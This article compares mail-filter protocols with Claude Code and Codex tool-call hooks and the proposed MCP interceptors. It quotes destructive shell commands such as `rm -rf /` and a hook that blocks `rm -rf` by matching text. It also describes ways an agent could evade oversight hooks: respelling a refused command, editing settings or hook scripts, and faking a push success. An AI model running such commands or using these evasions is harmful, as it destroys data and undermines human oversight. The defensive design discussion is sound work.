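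The protection is limited because "should", in internet standards, lets a server depart from the rule for a good reason, and because the rule covers only the verdict, not other edits. If one scanner removes Lee from the envelope and accepts the message, a later scanner can add Lee back. The server must check added addresses against its own policy, but that policy may not include the first scanner's reason for removing Lee. A scanner that needs its decision to stand should reject the message rather than try to repair it.

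The ranking also treats all stronger verdicts as safe. A later scanner may change "quarantine" to "discard". The sender then still gets a success code, but the administrator no longer has a message to review.

### Hooks on delivery

Milter has no equivalent of the outbound hooks. The server calls them after it tries to deliver a message, when some recipients still need another attempt, and when it is about to send a delivery notice such as a bounce. The scanner receives the result for each recipient and can cancel further attempts or suppress the notice.

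Outbound hooks run only after the first delivery attempt. In one of De Gennaro's examples, a message to three people has reached the first, is waiting to be retried for the second, and has failed for the third. A scanner could still stop the retry, but it could not recall the first copy. Outbound hooks are therefore useful for recording what an agent has sent, but any limit on what it may send must be enforced when the server receives the message from the agent.

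### Progress towards a standard

Stalwart is taking the proposal through the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which publishes the SMTP specification. De Gennaro's draft is an individual submission, which anyone may make, and has no formal standing. To get further, it needs a working group. Supporters usually form one by holding a "birds of a feather" (BOF) meeting, where they have to show that enough people want the work and will do it.

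After presentations at two IETF meetings, De Gennaro requested a BOF in April 2026. The request lists supporters from outside Stalwart, including people from Rspamd and the mail companies Fastmail and Heinlein, but only six to ten people had offered to join a working group. According to Stalwart's *MTA Hooks at the IETF* (2026), the responsible IETF director asked the supporters to build a community and write a charter first. The supporters hoped to be ready for the July meeting in Vienna, with an online session as the fallback.

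MTA Hooks was not among the five BOFs that the IETF (2026) scheduled for its July meeting in Vienna, three of which dealt at least partly with AI agents. The IETF announced two BOFs about mail for its November meeting. One of them, on improvements "in mail operations", could be about MTA Hooks but could equally be about another proposal, so it is uncertain whether the founding session has taken place. The May draft was due to expire on 9 November 2026 unless a newer version replaced it.

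The protocol is already in use, although it has not been standardized. De Gennaro reports that thousands of Stalwart installations use it, and Rspamd plans to support it. But Stalwart also argues that a protocol with only one mail server behind it "is not a protocol, it is an API", and MTA Hooks did not yet meet that test in mid-2026.

### Which repairs an agent interface would need

A written specification would be at least as useful for agents, because a company may want one policy service to check agents that run in several harnesses. The specification would have to be especially clear about errors. If a filter refuses a tool call and also makes an edit it has no permission for, the harness should drop the edit and keep the refusal.

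The rule that one filter cannot weaken another's verdict would carry over well to agents. The closest thing to quarantine is holding a tool call until a person approves it. A filter that recognises a familiar command should not be able to turn another filter's "ask a person" into "allow". The mail draft does not protect a filter's edits from later filters, but agents would need that protection too. If one filter removes a dangerous option from a shell command, a later filter could restore it, so the harness would have to rerun the earlier checks on the final version.

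HTTP also lets the filter run on a different machine, where an agent with shell access cannot easily alter it. The harness's settings would still need protection, since an agent that could edit them might remove the filter's address.

De Gennaro's advice that scanners should not depend on earlier calls is harder to apply to agents than to mail. One mail transaction is small enough to fit in a request, but an agent may make hundreds of tool calls, and some rules depend on their order. For example, enforcing a rule that an agent may not send outside mail after reading the payroll file requires a record of what the agent has read. Either the harness must send that history with every request, or the filter must store it.

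## Hooks that check a coding agent's tool calls

Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, lets users add their own checks, called hooks. A hook is a program or service that the harness runs at a set stage and whose decision it enforces. Like a milter, a hook receives a description of what is about to happen and can allow, refuse or change it.

Anthropic's *Hooks reference* describes five types of hook. A command hook is a local program that receives its input as JSON text and prints its answer. An HTTP hook exchanges the same JSON with a web service, much as MTA Hooks does. The other three types call a tool on an MCP server, ask a Claude model a question, or start a second agent to investigate. Claude Code starts a command hook afresh for each event, so the hook has to use a file to keep data between events. A milter keeps running and can hold data for the length of a connection.

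### The stages of a session

The reference lists 33 events that can trigger a hook, including changes of working directory or model. Six matter most for policy.

`SessionStart` runs when a session begins or resumes. The hook can add text for the model to read, such as the name of the current code branch, but it cannot block the session. `UserPromptSubmit` runs before the model processes a prompt. The hook can block the prompt or add text beside it, but cannot reword the prompt. Claude Code also runs this event for scheduled tasks and for messages from other sessions, so the prompt may not come from a person.

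`PreToolUse` runs after the model writes a tool call's arguments and before the harness carries out the call. `PermissionRequest` runs only when Claude Code is about to ask the user for permission, or when it needs to ask but cannot show the question. This hook can answer for the user, and it can save a permission rule so that the same question does not come up again.

`PostToolUse` runs after a tool has succeeded, and a separate event covers failures. The hook can replace the tool's output before the model reads it, but any files the tool wrote remain. It can also return "block", but the model still gets the original output, with the hook's reason next to it.

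A `Stop` hook runs when the agent has finished responding, and blocking at this point makes the agent keep working. For example, a hook could run the project's tests and block if any fail. To prevent an endless loop, Claude Code ends the turn after hooks have prolonged it eight times in a row without a tool call in between. Milter has no equivalent, because a mail filter can't make a client send another message.

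### Matching a hook to a tool

A user registers a hook in a settings file. This entry runs a script before certain shell commands:

```json
{
  "hooks": {
    "PreToolUse": [{
      "matcher": "Bash",
      "hooks": [{
        "if": "Bash(rm *)",
        "type": "command",
        "command": "/opt/policy/block-rm.sh"
      }]
    }]
  }
}
```

The `matcher` selects tools by name, and `Bash` is the tool that runs shell commands. If the matcher contains only letters, digits and a few other plain characters, it must match the tool's full name. Claude Code treats any other matcher as a regular expression, which can match any part of the name.

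Matchers are easy to get wrong for MCP tools, which have names such as `mcp__memory__create_entities`. The matcher `mcp__memory` matches no tool, so a user who wants to cover the whole memory server has to write `mcp__memory__.*`. Matching too many tools is a less serious mistake. For example, `Edit.*` also matches `NotebookEdit`, so the hook runs too often. A hook that never runs is harder to notice because it looks the same as one that runs and allows every call.

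The optional `if` condition limits a hook to calls with certain arguments. Claude Code splits compound commands and checks inside substitutions, so `echo $(rm -rf /)` starts the script above. If it can't determine what a command will run, it starts the hook anyway. Anthropic still describes the condition as best-effort and recommends the permission settings for a hard rule. A cautious user can omit the condition and have the script examine every shell command, though this starts a process each time.

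A milter negotiates with the server over which stages it will receive, whereas the settings file determines which events a hook receives. A matcher for one tool doesn't cover other tools with the same effect, so a matcher for the file-editing tool misses a shell command that edits a file.

### What the hook receives

For a tool call, the JSON input includes the session ID, the working directory, the permission mode, and the tool's name and arguments. If a subagent (a helper that the main agent started) made the call, the input also identifies the subagent.

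As in mail, some of the information a hook receives is more reliable than the rest. The harness supplies the working directory and the permission mode, while the model writes the arguments. A shell call can include a `description` of what the command does, and a hook should give it about as much weight as a milter gives the HELO name. For MCP tools, Claude Code adds the server's name and the source of its definition, such as the user's settings or a plugin. Anthropic advises basing trust on the source, not the name. The source is similar to a mail client's login name, and the server's name to the MAIL FROM address.

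For the tools that read and write files, Claude Code converts every path to an absolute one before the hook runs, so a rule that protects a directory doesn't have to handle `~` or relative paths. Milter authors have to handle variant forms of recipient addresses themselves. Shell commands are harder to check because the hook gets the whole command, including any paths, as a string.

The input also includes the path to the session's transcript. A hook could search it to enforce a rule that depends on earlier calls, such as the one against sending outside mail after reading the payroll file. But Claude Code writes the transcript with a delay, so if the agent sends the mail right after reading the file, the read may not be in the transcript when the hook checks it. A hook can avoid this problem by keeping its own record of the agent's calls.

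### The possible answers

A `PreToolUse` hook can return one of four decisions, or none:

- `allow` skips the question that Claude Code would otherwise put to the user.
- `deny` cancels the call and gives the model the hook's reason.
- `ask` shows the user a permission prompt with the hook's reason and a label for where the hook came from.
- `defer` ends the turn and saves the call, so that another program can resume it later.

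If the hook returns no decision, the call goes through the normal permission checks. This is close to milter's "continue". A hook that only looks for bad commands should return no decision on all other commands, because returning `allow` would remove the user's chance to object to them.

`defer` works only when another program runs Claude Code without a user at the terminal, and only if the model has made a single tool call in that turn. If the agent needs an answer from a customer, for example, the hook defers the call and the outer program collects the answer in its own interface. Claude Code then resumes the session and runs the hook again on the same call, and the hook returns `allow` with the answer. The deferral has no time limit, but Claude Code deletes saved sessions after 30 days by default.

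A hook can also supply changed arguments in a field called `updatedInput`. The field replaces the whole set of arguments, so the hook must include any that stay the same, much as a milter must supply a complete new body to correct one word. If the hook also returns `allow`, the changed call runs without a prompt, while `ask` shows the user the changed version. An example in Anthropic's *Intercept and control agent behavior with hooks*, which covers hooks written as functions inside an application, adds `/sandbox` to the start of the path of every file the agent writes.

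### Refusing a destructive shell command

Anthropic's main worked example uses a script like the one in the settings above. The agent proposes the shell command `rm -rf /tmp/build`, which would delete a build directory and everything in it without asking for confirmation.

The harness has not run anything yet. It raises the `PreToolUse` event, and the matcher `Bash` fits the tool's name. The `if` condition fits too, because the command begins with `rm`. Claude Code starts the script and passes it the call, shortened here:

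```json
{
  "hook_event_name": "PreToolUse",
  "tool_name": "Bash",
  "tool_input": {"command": "rm -rf /tmp/build"}
}
```

The script extracts the command, searches it for the text `rm -rf`, and prints its decision:

```json
{
  "hookSpecificOutput": {
    "hookEventName": "PreToolUse",
    "permissionDecision": "deny",
    "permissionDecisionReason": "Destructive command blocked by hook"
  }
}
```

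Claude Code cancels the call, leaving the directory in place, and gives the model the reason. The model can then try another action. A script can also refuse a call more simply, by exiting with status 2 and writing the reason to its error output. By default, a hook that crashes or times out does not stop the call.

For `npm test`, the `if` condition fails and the script never starts. For `rm file.txt`, the script starts but doesn't find the text, so it exits without a decision. The call then goes to the permission checks, which may still prompt the user.

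The script is a demonstration and would make a poor policy. It searches for `rm -rf`, so it would miss `rm -fr /tmp/build`, which does the same thing. A milter that searches messages for a phrase has the same weakness, but an agent that has just received a refusal has a reason to try another spelling.

The reason "Destructive command blocked by hook" could be more useful if it also included what the model may do instead. The same applies to the text of a 550 reply, but the model reads the hook's reason directly and can act on it in its next step.

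### Several hooks on one call

Milters run one after another, but Claude Code runs all the hooks that match an event in parallel. Anthropic notes that each hook runs to completion even if another has already refused the call. A hook with side effects may therefore act on a call that never goes ahead. If one hook logs every command and another refuses `rm -rf`, the log will include commands that never ran. Similarly, a hook that sends a notification for each deployment may send one for a deployment that was refused.

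Claude Code then applies the most restrictive decision. From most to least restrictive, the decisions are `deny`, `defer`, `ask` and `allow`. The order of the hooks in the settings file makes no difference. MTA Hooks ranks its verdicts for the same purpose, but Claude Code's method is simpler because its hooks don't edit a shared verdict.

The design is weaker when hooks change a tool call's arguments. If two hooks return different versions, Claude Code uses only one and doesn't guarantee which. Suppose the agent proposes `curl -k https://example.com/data`, where `-k` switches off the check of the site's certificate. One hook removes `-k`, and another adds a time limit. Both start from the model's original command and return a complete replacement. If Claude Code uses the second version, the download has a time limit but still skips the certificate check. Anthropic advises against having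 more than one hook rewrite the same tool's input. A hook that enforces a security rule would do better to refuse the call, because a refusal blocks it regardless of what other hooks return.

Because hooks run in parallel, they also can't check each other's changes. If one hook redirects a file to a new path, a hook that protects certain directories still receives the path the model wrote. In a chain of milters, the later filter would receive the changed message.

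Claude Code partly makes up for this by applying its permission rules to the changed arguments. In its "auto" mode, where a classifier reviews actions in place of the user, it may also refuse a call that a hook changed after the review. The model can then submit the changed version as a new call. If it does so immediately and without altering it, Claude Code ignores any further changes from the hook, so the version that runs is the one the classifier reviewed. Even in sessions where this applies, however, command hooks in a settings file can usually change shell commands and file edits without such a refusal.

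### Hooks and the permission settings

Claude Code has its own permission rules for denying a call, asking the user about it, or allowing it. According to Anthropic, it checks deny rules first, then ask rules, then allow rules, and applies the first one that matches. A rule that denies every `aws` command therefore blocks `aws s3 ls`, even if a narrower rule allows it.

A hook can make these rules stricter but not looser. If it returns `allow`, a matching deny rule still blocks the call and a matching ask rule still prompts the user. If it returns `deny`, it blocks the call even when an allow rule matches, and even in the mode that skips permission prompts. Postfix combines its access table with its milters in much the same way.

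A user can let an agent run most shell commands without asking by allowing the `Bash` tool as a whole and having a hook refuse the exceptions. Denying `Bash` and having a hook allow exceptions doesn't work, because a hook cannot override a deny rule. In plan mode, where the agent is supposed to plan before changing anything, a hook's `allow` has no effect on file edits or other calls that do more than read.

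Mods are a notable exception to the rule. Anthropic uses this name for plugins that run functions inside Claude Code's own process, whereas Sendmail's developers chose a separate process for filters. A mod's decision comes after those of the `PreToolUse` hooks, and it can approve a call that a hook has refused if the machine has no centrally managed settings and the session doesn't use a company login. Otherwise, the hook's refusal stands by default.

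Managed settings also give a company control similar to a mail administrator's. Users can add their own hooks but can't turn off the managed ones, and the company can block all other hooks.

### Milter and hooks side by side

The table pairs each milter stage and verdict with its closest equivalent in Claude Code. The early stages match only loosely, because a session is not an SMTP connection.

| Milter | Nearest hook counterpart | Main difference |
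|---|---|---|
| Negotiation | `matcher` and `if` in the settings file | The hook requests nothing and declares nothing |
| Connect and HELO | `SessionStart` | The hook cannot refuse the session |
| MAIL FROM | `UserPromptSubmit` | The hook can add text for the model |
| RCPT TO | None | The hook receives the whole call at once |
| DATA, headers and body | None | The hook receives the whole call at once |
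| End of message | `PreToolUse` | The hook has had no earlier stage of the same call |
| Abort | `StopFailure`, in part | Runs after an API error but not after a user's interruption |
| Close | `SessionEnd` | None that matters for policy |
| Unrecognised command | None | Claude Code rejects unknown tools before any hook runs |
| Continue | No decision | The permission rules apply next |
| Accept | `allow` | Skips a question to the user, not the remaining stages |
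| Reject | `deny` | Always applies to the whole call |
| Temporary failure | `defer` | The harness keeps the call, whereas a mail client keeps the message |
| Discard | None | The model gets a reason for every refusal |
| Skip | None | The input does not arrive in blocks |
| No reply | A hook that runs in the background | A milter can still refuse at a later stage, but the background hook cannot |
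| Quarantine | `ask` | The agent waits for the decision, whereas a mail client gets a success code |
| Changes to the message | `updatedInput` | Any `PreToolUse` hook may make them |

`PostToolUse` has no row because a milter's work ends when the server accepts the message.

The lack of a discard verdict is an advantage, given the trouble that silent loss causes in mail. A hook author could still build one by using a `PreToolUse` hook to replace `git push` with a command that does nothing, and a `PostToolUse` hook to replace the empty output with a success message. The agent would then tell its user that the code was published. Anthropic warns that even removing error details from a result can lead the model to proceed on a false assumption.

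A hook cannot refuse only part of a tool call. Suppose the report agent writes to Dana and Lee through a tool that takes a list of recipients. The milter could refuse Lee alone, but a hook has to either deny the whole call or return a new list without Lee. If it denies the call, Dana gets nothing until the agent tries again. If it removes Lee, Dana gets the report straight away, but the tool then reports success and the agent may believe that Lee has it too. The hook should therefore add a note saying that it removed Lee and why. Similarly, a hook can't refuse only the `git push` in `npm test && git push`.

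Unlike milters, hooks don't declare in advance what they may change. A hook meant only to log commands could return new arguments for any of them. For a command hook, a declaration would add little protection, because whoever controls the program can already run code on the user's machine. It would be more useful for an HTTP hook on another machine, which can affect the agent only through its responses.

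### What hooks add

A mail filter can't ask a person in the middle of an SMTP conversation, because the client is waiting for a reply and will eventually give up. A coding agent's user is often at the keyboard, so a hook can use `ask` to refer a doubtful command to someone who knows the purpose of the work. Rules can then be less exact, because a wrong guess leads to a question rather than a failed task. If Claude Code runs with nobody to answer, it refuses the call and gives the model the hook's reason.

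`PermissionRequest` hooks run when Claude Code is about to ask the user for permission, and they can answer for the user. This suggests that a hook that approves permission requests could answer a question that a `PreToolUse` hook meant for a human. A company that relies on `ask` for human review should check which hooks are registered for `PermissionRequest`.

Hooks can also attach a note for the model to a successful call, for example that the agent has just edited a generated file and should change its source instead. The note corrects the agent without blocking it. A milter can choose the wording of a refusal, but it has no good way to tell the sender anything when it lets a message through. Anthropic recommends phrasing hook notes as facts, because text that reads like a system command can set off Claude's defences against prompt injection. The hook's developer also has to be careful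 about what goes into the note, because an attacker may have written text that the hook copies from a web page.

### Codex

OpenAI's Codex has a very similar interface. *Codex CLI Hooks After GA* (Vaughan, 2026) dates the interface's general release to 14 May 2026 and counts ten events, including all six of the main stages described above, under the same names. The sample settings in *Async Hooks and MCP Tool Hooks in Codex CLI v0.148.0* (Vaughan, 2026) have the same layout of event, matcher and handler as Claude Code's. Tool names can differ, so anyone moving a hook from one agent to the other has to check its matcher. Codex, for example, edits files with a tool called `apply_patch`.

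*Codex CLI Hooks* (Vaughan, 2026) states that a `PreToolUse` hook can refuse a call or add context, and that `PostToolUse` cannot undo side effects. According to OpenAI, Codex starts all matching hooks at the same time, so one hook cannot prevent another from starting. So neither company uses milter's fixed order.

Codex also requires someone to review and trust a command hook before it runs, unless the hook comes from managed settings. Vaughan says this trust is based on a hash, a short fingerprint computed from data, so a changed hook would presumably need a new review. The review is useful because some hooks may be stored in the directories where the coding agent works. But if the hash covered only the settings entry, an agent could edit the script that the entry names without triggering a new review.

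## Interceptors for the Model Context Protocol

Claude Code and Codex each have their own hooks. A proposed extension to MCP would instead give agents one shared interface for filters, which it calls interceptors. Sambhav Kothari of Bloomberg filed it in November 2025 as Specification Enhancement Proposal 1763 (SEP-1763), and the work continues in pull request 2624. The proposal is the closest agent counterpart to milter, because any harness or tool server could consult filters that other people wrote. In late 2026 it was still only a proposal, with experimental code.

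### Many clients, many filters

The Model Context Protocol's *Interceptors Charter*, which set up a working group on the proposal, describes "a sprawling landscape of sidecars, proxies, and gateways" that mostly cannot be reused. A sidecar is a helper program that runs beside another program, and a gateway is a network service that an agent's traffic passes through. Companies use both to check what agents do, but each product has its own interface.

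The charter calls this an M × N problem. In MCP, the client is the part of the harness that talks to tool servers. If M clients each have their own interface, developers have to write M × N connections to make N filters work with all of them. With a shared interface, they write only one for each client and one for each filter, so five clients and eight filters would take 13 connections instead of 40.

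The existing interfaces differ. AWS's *Types of interceptors* describes request and response filters for Amazon's gateway, whose input format depends on the kind of service behind the gateway. LangChain, which makes software for building agents, has a filter interface that wraps each MCP tool call in a function that can change the tool's name, its arguments and the HTTP headers. A program that removes personal data from tool calls would need separate versions for Amazon, LangChain and Claude Code. Postfix adopted milter to avoid the same duplication.

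The working group does not plan to standardise how Claude Code or any other harness runs its hooks internally. A harness could keep its own hooks and also use interceptors.

### Events and phases

An interceptor applies to one or more lifecycle events, most of which are operations MCP already defines. The most important is `tools/call`, where the client asks a server to run a tool. Others include listing the server's tools, reading data the server offers, and elicitation, where the server asks the user a question through the client.

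Each event has a request phase and a response phase. For a tool call, these phases correspond to Claude Code's `PreToolUse` and `PostToolUse`. The response to `tools/list` is also worth checking, because it gives the model tool descriptions that the server's operator can change. A filter could remove a suspicious tool before its description reaches the model.

An interceptor's entry could look like this, with field names from an April 2026 revision of the proposal:

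```json
{
  "name": "internal-only",
  "type": "validation",
  "hook": {"events": ["tools/call"], "phase": "request"},
  "mode": "enforce"
}
```

Like milter's negotiation, the entry specifies which stages the filter needs. An interceptor can also use `*` to select every event or `*/request` to select all requests.

Among other changes, that revision removed the detailed data formats for each event (Degiorgio, 2026, *Updated SEP*). This matters little for tool calls, because MCP already defines their format. But the working group also wants interceptors to cover events outside MCP, such as the harness's requests to the language model, which differ between harnesses. Unless clients agree on a format for these requests, a filter for them will still need a separate version for each client.

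### Validators and mutators

The proposal has two types of interceptor: validators, which return a verdict on the data but cannot change it, and mutators, which change the data but return no verdict.

*Interceptors for MCP* (Degiorgio and Chan, 2026), a set of slides from Bloomberg, gives examples of both validators and mutators. One validator blocks text that contains a US social security number, another finds a missing comma in JSON, and a third finds an undefined variable in code. One mutator replaces the social security number with "[REDACTED]", and another adds background facts to a text.

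Bloomberg itself uses interceptors more for quality than for security. In the slides, a validator checks whether the research cited in an AI answer exists. If it doesn't, the validator rejects the answer and notifies the agent. A mutator adds material such as recent news and earnings dates to a user's question about a company's shares.

A validator's result can be more detailed than pass or fail. The project's Go code, documented in *chain* (2026), counts errors, warnings and informational messages separately. Presumably only an error should stop a call, so a validator could use a warning to report an unusual command without blocking it.

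Validators have no equivalent of milter's "accept" or Claude Code's `allow`. A passing result means only that the call passed that validator's checks, so one validator cannot exempt a call from another's. Validators also have no equivalent of `ask`, so they can't hold an uncertain call for a person to review. The harness would need its own way to do that.

The two types are not completely distinct, because a mutator can still stop a call by failing. The Go code has a separate status for a chain that ended this way. A mutator could therefore return an error on purpose when it receives data it can't safely repair, although its type suggests that it never blocks anything.

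### Finding and calling interceptors

An MCP server can host interceptors as well as tools. The model decides when to call a tool, but the client or server software calls an interceptor whenever a matching event occurs. The interceptor can run in the same process, as a sidecar, or on another machine.

The software first sends `interceptors/list` to find out which interceptors a server hosts. When a matching event occurs, it sends `interceptor/invoke` with the data to check. The request can also carry settings for that interceptor and a time limit.

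The original proposal had another command that asked a server to run a whole series of interceptors, but the April revision removed it. The calling software now fetches the lists, merges and sorts them, calls each interceptor and combines the results, usually using a library. This resembles milter, where the mail server runs the series and each filter returns only its own result. Two clients could therefore run the same interceptors slightly differently, as Sendmail and Postfix do with milters.

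Automatic discovery carries a risk that milter does not have, since a mail administrator lists each filter by hand. In the Go code, adding an MCP server to a chain adds every interceptor that the server hosts. If a company adds a server to get its address checker, and the server also offers a mutator for every event, that mutator could read and rewrite all the traffic in the chain. The code lets the caller limit a run to named interceptors, and a cautious company should use that option.

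The interceptor's author also has some influence over the order, whereas in milter the administrator sets it. Each mutator has a number called `priorityHint`, and the Go code runs mutators from the lowest number to the highest, breaking ties alphabetically. An author who wants a mutator to run last can give it a very high number.

### The order of work

The order depends on whether the software is sending data or receiving it:

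- When sending, it runs the mutators, then the validators, and then sends the data.
- When receiving, it runs the validators, then the mutators, and then uses the data.

In both cases the validators are next to the trust boundary, where data passes between software that one party controls and software that it does not. They check outgoing data in its final form and incoming data before any mutator handles it. A tool call from a client to a server can therefore go through mutators and then validators on the client's side, followed by validators and then mutators on the server's side. The response takes the same route in reverse.

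Mutators run one at a time because each works on the previous one's result. Validators change nothing, so they can all run at once and together take only as long as the slowest one. Degiorgio and Chan also describe mutations as "atomic", which presumably means that a call never goes out with only some of its changes.

When two Claude Code hooks rewrite the same command, only one rewrite survives. If the hooks were mutators, the second would rewrite the first one's result, so the command would have both changes.

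The receiving order has a weakness, because no validator on that side checks what the mutators produce. Suppose a client's validators find no prompt injection in a search result. If a mutator then adds recent news from another website, the model reads it unchecked. To prevent this, the mutator's author would have to check the news separately, or the client would have to run the validators again.

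Developers can also easily use one side's order on the other. The April version of the Go code always validates requests before changing them, which is correct for a server receiving a call. If a client used the same function for calls it was about to send, its mutators would run after its validators, and the client would send the call without checking their changes.

### An email through four interceptors

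Suppose the report agent from the earlier examples sends its mail through an MCP tool, and the model writes this call:

```json
{
  "name": "send_email",
  "arguments": {
    "to": ["dana@example.com"],
    "subject": "Weekly report",
    "body": "Refund issued to customer 123-45-6789."
  }
}
```

The company has four interceptors for the request phase of `tools/call`. The client is sending, so the mutators run first.

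| Order | Interceptor | What it does | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | `redact-ids`, mutator, priority 10 | Looks for identity numbers in the body | Replaces the number with "[REDACTED]" |
| 2 | `copy-supervisor`, mutator, priority 20 | Adds the supervisor to the recipients | Adds sam@example.com |
| 3 | `internal-only`, validator | Checks that every address is at example.com | Pass |
| 3 | `no-ids`, validator | Looks for identity numbers anywhere in the call | Pass |

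The client then sends this version to the mail tool's server:

```json
{
  "name": "send_email",
  "arguments": {
    "to": ["dana@example.com", "sam@example.com"],
    "subject": "Weekly report",
    "body": "Refund issued to customer [REDACTED]."
  }
}
```

The `no-ids` check is useful even after `redact-ids` because it covers the whole call. If the model had put the number in the subject line, the mutator would have missed it and the validator would have stopped the email.

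The order also protects the company from mistakes in its own filters. If an administrator had entered the supervisor's address as sam@example.net, `internal-only` would have refused the call. A chain of milters could miss that mistake, because the other filters don't check added recipients.

Like a Claude Code hook, a validator can't refuse one recipient and allow the others. If the model had included lee@example.net, `internal-only` would have refused the entire call, and Dana would not have received the report either.

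### Audit mode

Each interceptor runs in either "enforce" or "audit" mode. In audit mode, a validator records what it would have refused but blocks nothing, and a mutator computes and records its change but doesn't apply it.

A company could run `internal-only` in audit mode for a week and find that the agent regularly writes to an outside accountant. It could then add the accountant's address to the permitted list and switch the validator to "enforce". A milter's author can imitate audit mode by logging what the milter would have refused and returning "continue" instead, but each milter then needs its own setting to switch between auditing and enforcing.

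The original proposal had a third type of interceptor, for observation only. Kurt Degiorgio of Bloomberg replaced it with audit mode, and Peder Holdgaard Pedersen of Saxo Bank, another leader of the working group, objected. Pedersen argued that three types would be simpler, and that it is strange to run a validator or mutator with no effect, since its result is supposed to matter. He also thought that observers would be hard to order if they were actually validators or mutators.

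Degiorgio replied that reviewers of the first version had not wanted a rival to OpenTelemetry, an established standard for collecting data about running software. A separate observer would also have to be rewritten as a validator before it could enforce anything, whereas switching from audit mode to enforcement takes a change to one field. And an observer could not test a mutator, because it cannot record the change the mutator would make.

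Degiorgio has the better argument for testing new rules, but the order Pedersen points out does make logging difficult. When a client sends a call, its mutators run before its validators, so a logger built as a validator in audit mode would record the email with "[REDACTED]" in it. To record what the model wrote, the company would have to build the logger as a mutator in audit mode and give it the lowest priority number.

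Testing a mutator in audit mode also can't reveal that a validator would reject the changed version, because the change does not reach the later interceptors. If `copy-supervisor` had the wrong address and ran in audit mode, every email would pass `internal-only`, which would start refusing emails only when the company switched the mutator on.

### Kubernetes admission controllers

The proposal names Kubernetes admission controllers among its inspirations. Kubernetes is software that runs programs across a cluster of machines, and every change to the cluster goes through its central API server. After checking who is making the request and whether they have permission, the server passes the change to the admission controllers before storing it. Mutating controllers run first, one after another, and can modify the change, for example by adding a memory limit to a program that lacks one. Validating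 controllers then check the result in parallel, and a single refusal blocks the change. Companies can add their own controllers as web services to enforce local rules without altering Kubernetes.

The two types of interceptor, and the rule about which run in sequence and which in parallel, closely follow this model, but the order for receiving data is different. The Kubernetes server changes incoming requests before validating them, so its validators check exactly what it will store. An MCP server would validate incoming requests first and then change them. That order makes sense if the validators' main job is to keep hostile data away from everything that runs after them, but it means they don't check the final version of the request.

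Admission controllers also don't check requests that only read from the cluster. Interceptors need to check reads, because anything an agent reads could contain a prompt injection.

Degiorgio and Chan cite Amazon's Bedrock AgentCore, Claude Code's hooks and OpenAI's Guardrails as signs that the industry needs something similar. Milter is not among these products or the proposal's inspirations, although it is more than a decade older than Kubernetes. Milter and interceptors therefore seem to resemble each other because they address similar problems, and some of the people designing interceptors may be unfamiliar with mail administrators' experience.

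### Judging and changing in one filter

A single milter can both change messages and reject them. A virus scanner, for example, can remove an infected attachment from one message and reject another. With interceptors, the company would need a mutator to remove attachments and a validator to reject messages, and both would have to scan the same file.

The split can also leave the validator without information it could have used. After `redact-ids` has run, `no-ids` cannot determine whether the model tried to send one identity number or five hundred. A milter could count the numbers before redacting them and refuse the message if there were too many. Under the proposal, the mutator would have to keep the count and return an error.

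In exchange, a company can tell from a filter's type whether it might alter anything. The company can try an unfamiliar validator without worrying that it will redirect mail, although the validator still receives the contents. Milter's declarations are more precise for mutators, because they list the kinds of change a filter may make. The proposal's type field shows only that a mutator makes changes, so a mutator meant to redact the body could also replace the recipients. A validator on the sending side may catch this, but only if it has a rule about recipients.

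### Progress by late 2026

The working group's charter is dated 21 April 2026. Three of the group's four leaders work at Bloomberg, and the fourth is Pedersen. According to MCP Hangar's *ADR-005* (2026), a design record from a separate software project, the original issue closed on 22 April and pull request 2624 replaced it.

The proposal had not been accepted by the end of November. The Model Context Protocol's index of accepted and final proposals listed neither number, and the working group's page still listed an accepted proposal among its goals. The protocol's *MCP Extensions* gives the interceptor code as an example of an experimental extension, so the developers may change any part of it at any time.

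The extension needs the approval of MCP's core maintainers to move to the next stage, beta. Model Context Protocol's *SEP Guidelines* require a working prototype and a sponsor, which is normally a working group. The prototype exists, and the interceptors group could presumably act as sponsor. To then become stable, the extension would need a client and a server that work together and come from independent developers. Even then, it would be off by default.

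Low priority may be the larger obstacle. The project's roadmap, updated on 16 November, lists five priority areas, none of which includes interceptors (Model Context Protocol, 2026). Proposals outside those areas face a longer wait and must meet a higher standard. This fits poorly with the project's security plans, since a Model Context Protocol security group calls interceptors "the primary enforcement point for runtime security decisions".

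The draft will also need updating. It has servers announce their interceptors in MCP's opening handshake, but the protocol's July 2026 release removed that handshake, along with protocol-level sessions. Sampling, in which a server requests text from the client's model, is one of the events the charter lists, but the project has begun to retire it.

The code is further along than the approval. In April the working group was working on implementations in Go and C#. Model Context Protocol's *MCP Interceptors* (2026) explains that the Go version needed its own copy of the standard MCP library to add the new commands. The group also planned a general-purpose sidecar, but it was still only an idea.

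MCP Hangar already had a sidecar of this kind, which inspects all MCP traffic passing through it and can block calls. In May its developers decided to follow the proposal, and they had already added mutators and the `interceptors/list` command. The sidecar works with clients that don't support interceptors because it sits between the client and the tool server. Mail administrators once chained whole servers together in a similar way, but the first server accepted each message before the next one received it. An MCP sidecar can refuse a call before it reaches the tool server, and the client gets the refusal as the reply to its call.

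## When the filter is slow or fails

A server or harness that waits for a filter's verdict needs a rule for what to do if the filter crashes, hangs or can't be reached. Letting the traffic through is called failing open, and stopping it is called failing closed. A milder way for a mail server to fail closed is to tell the client to try again later.

### Postfix's four default actions

Postfix has four possible actions for mail whose milter has failed:

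- `tempfail`, the default, gives the client a temporary error.
- `accept` treats the mail as though the filter did not exist.
- `reject` refuses the mail permanently.
- `quarantine` accepts the message but freezes it in a "hold" queue.

Suppose a company's virus scanner crashes just as a customer's mail server is sending Dana a message. Under `tempfail`, the customer's server gets a 4xx code. It is still responsible for the message, so it keeps its copy and tries again later. If an administrator restarts the scanner within the hour, the scanner checks the message on the next attempt, and Dana gets it late. The `reject` setting would have bounced every message from that hour, and `accept` would have let them all through unscanned.

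This works only if the client has a queue. Mail servers have one, but an agent's mail tool may be a short script that treats a 4xx code as a plain failure. The report then isn't delivered until something sends it again.

Since version 3.0, Postfix has also let administrators set the default action and time limits separately for each milter. Its documentation gives the example of a "non-critical" milter set to `accept`, with a ten-second limit on connecting. A company could use those settings for the filter that adds a footer and leave the virus scanner on `tempfail`. Some vendors prefer to fail open. Danami's *Milter Settings*, which documents a mail filter that works with Postfix, gives `accept` as the default when the milter is down. Customers keep getting mail during an outage, but they may not notice for some time that nothing is checking it.

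### Time limits and duplicates

A filter that hangs is harder to deal with than one that crashes, because the server needs a limit on how long it waits. Postfix's limits are 30 seconds for the connect stage and for commands such as MAIL and RCPT, and 300 seconds for the headers, body and end of message. According to the Postfix documentation, 30 seconds may be too short for a filter that looks up many internet names.

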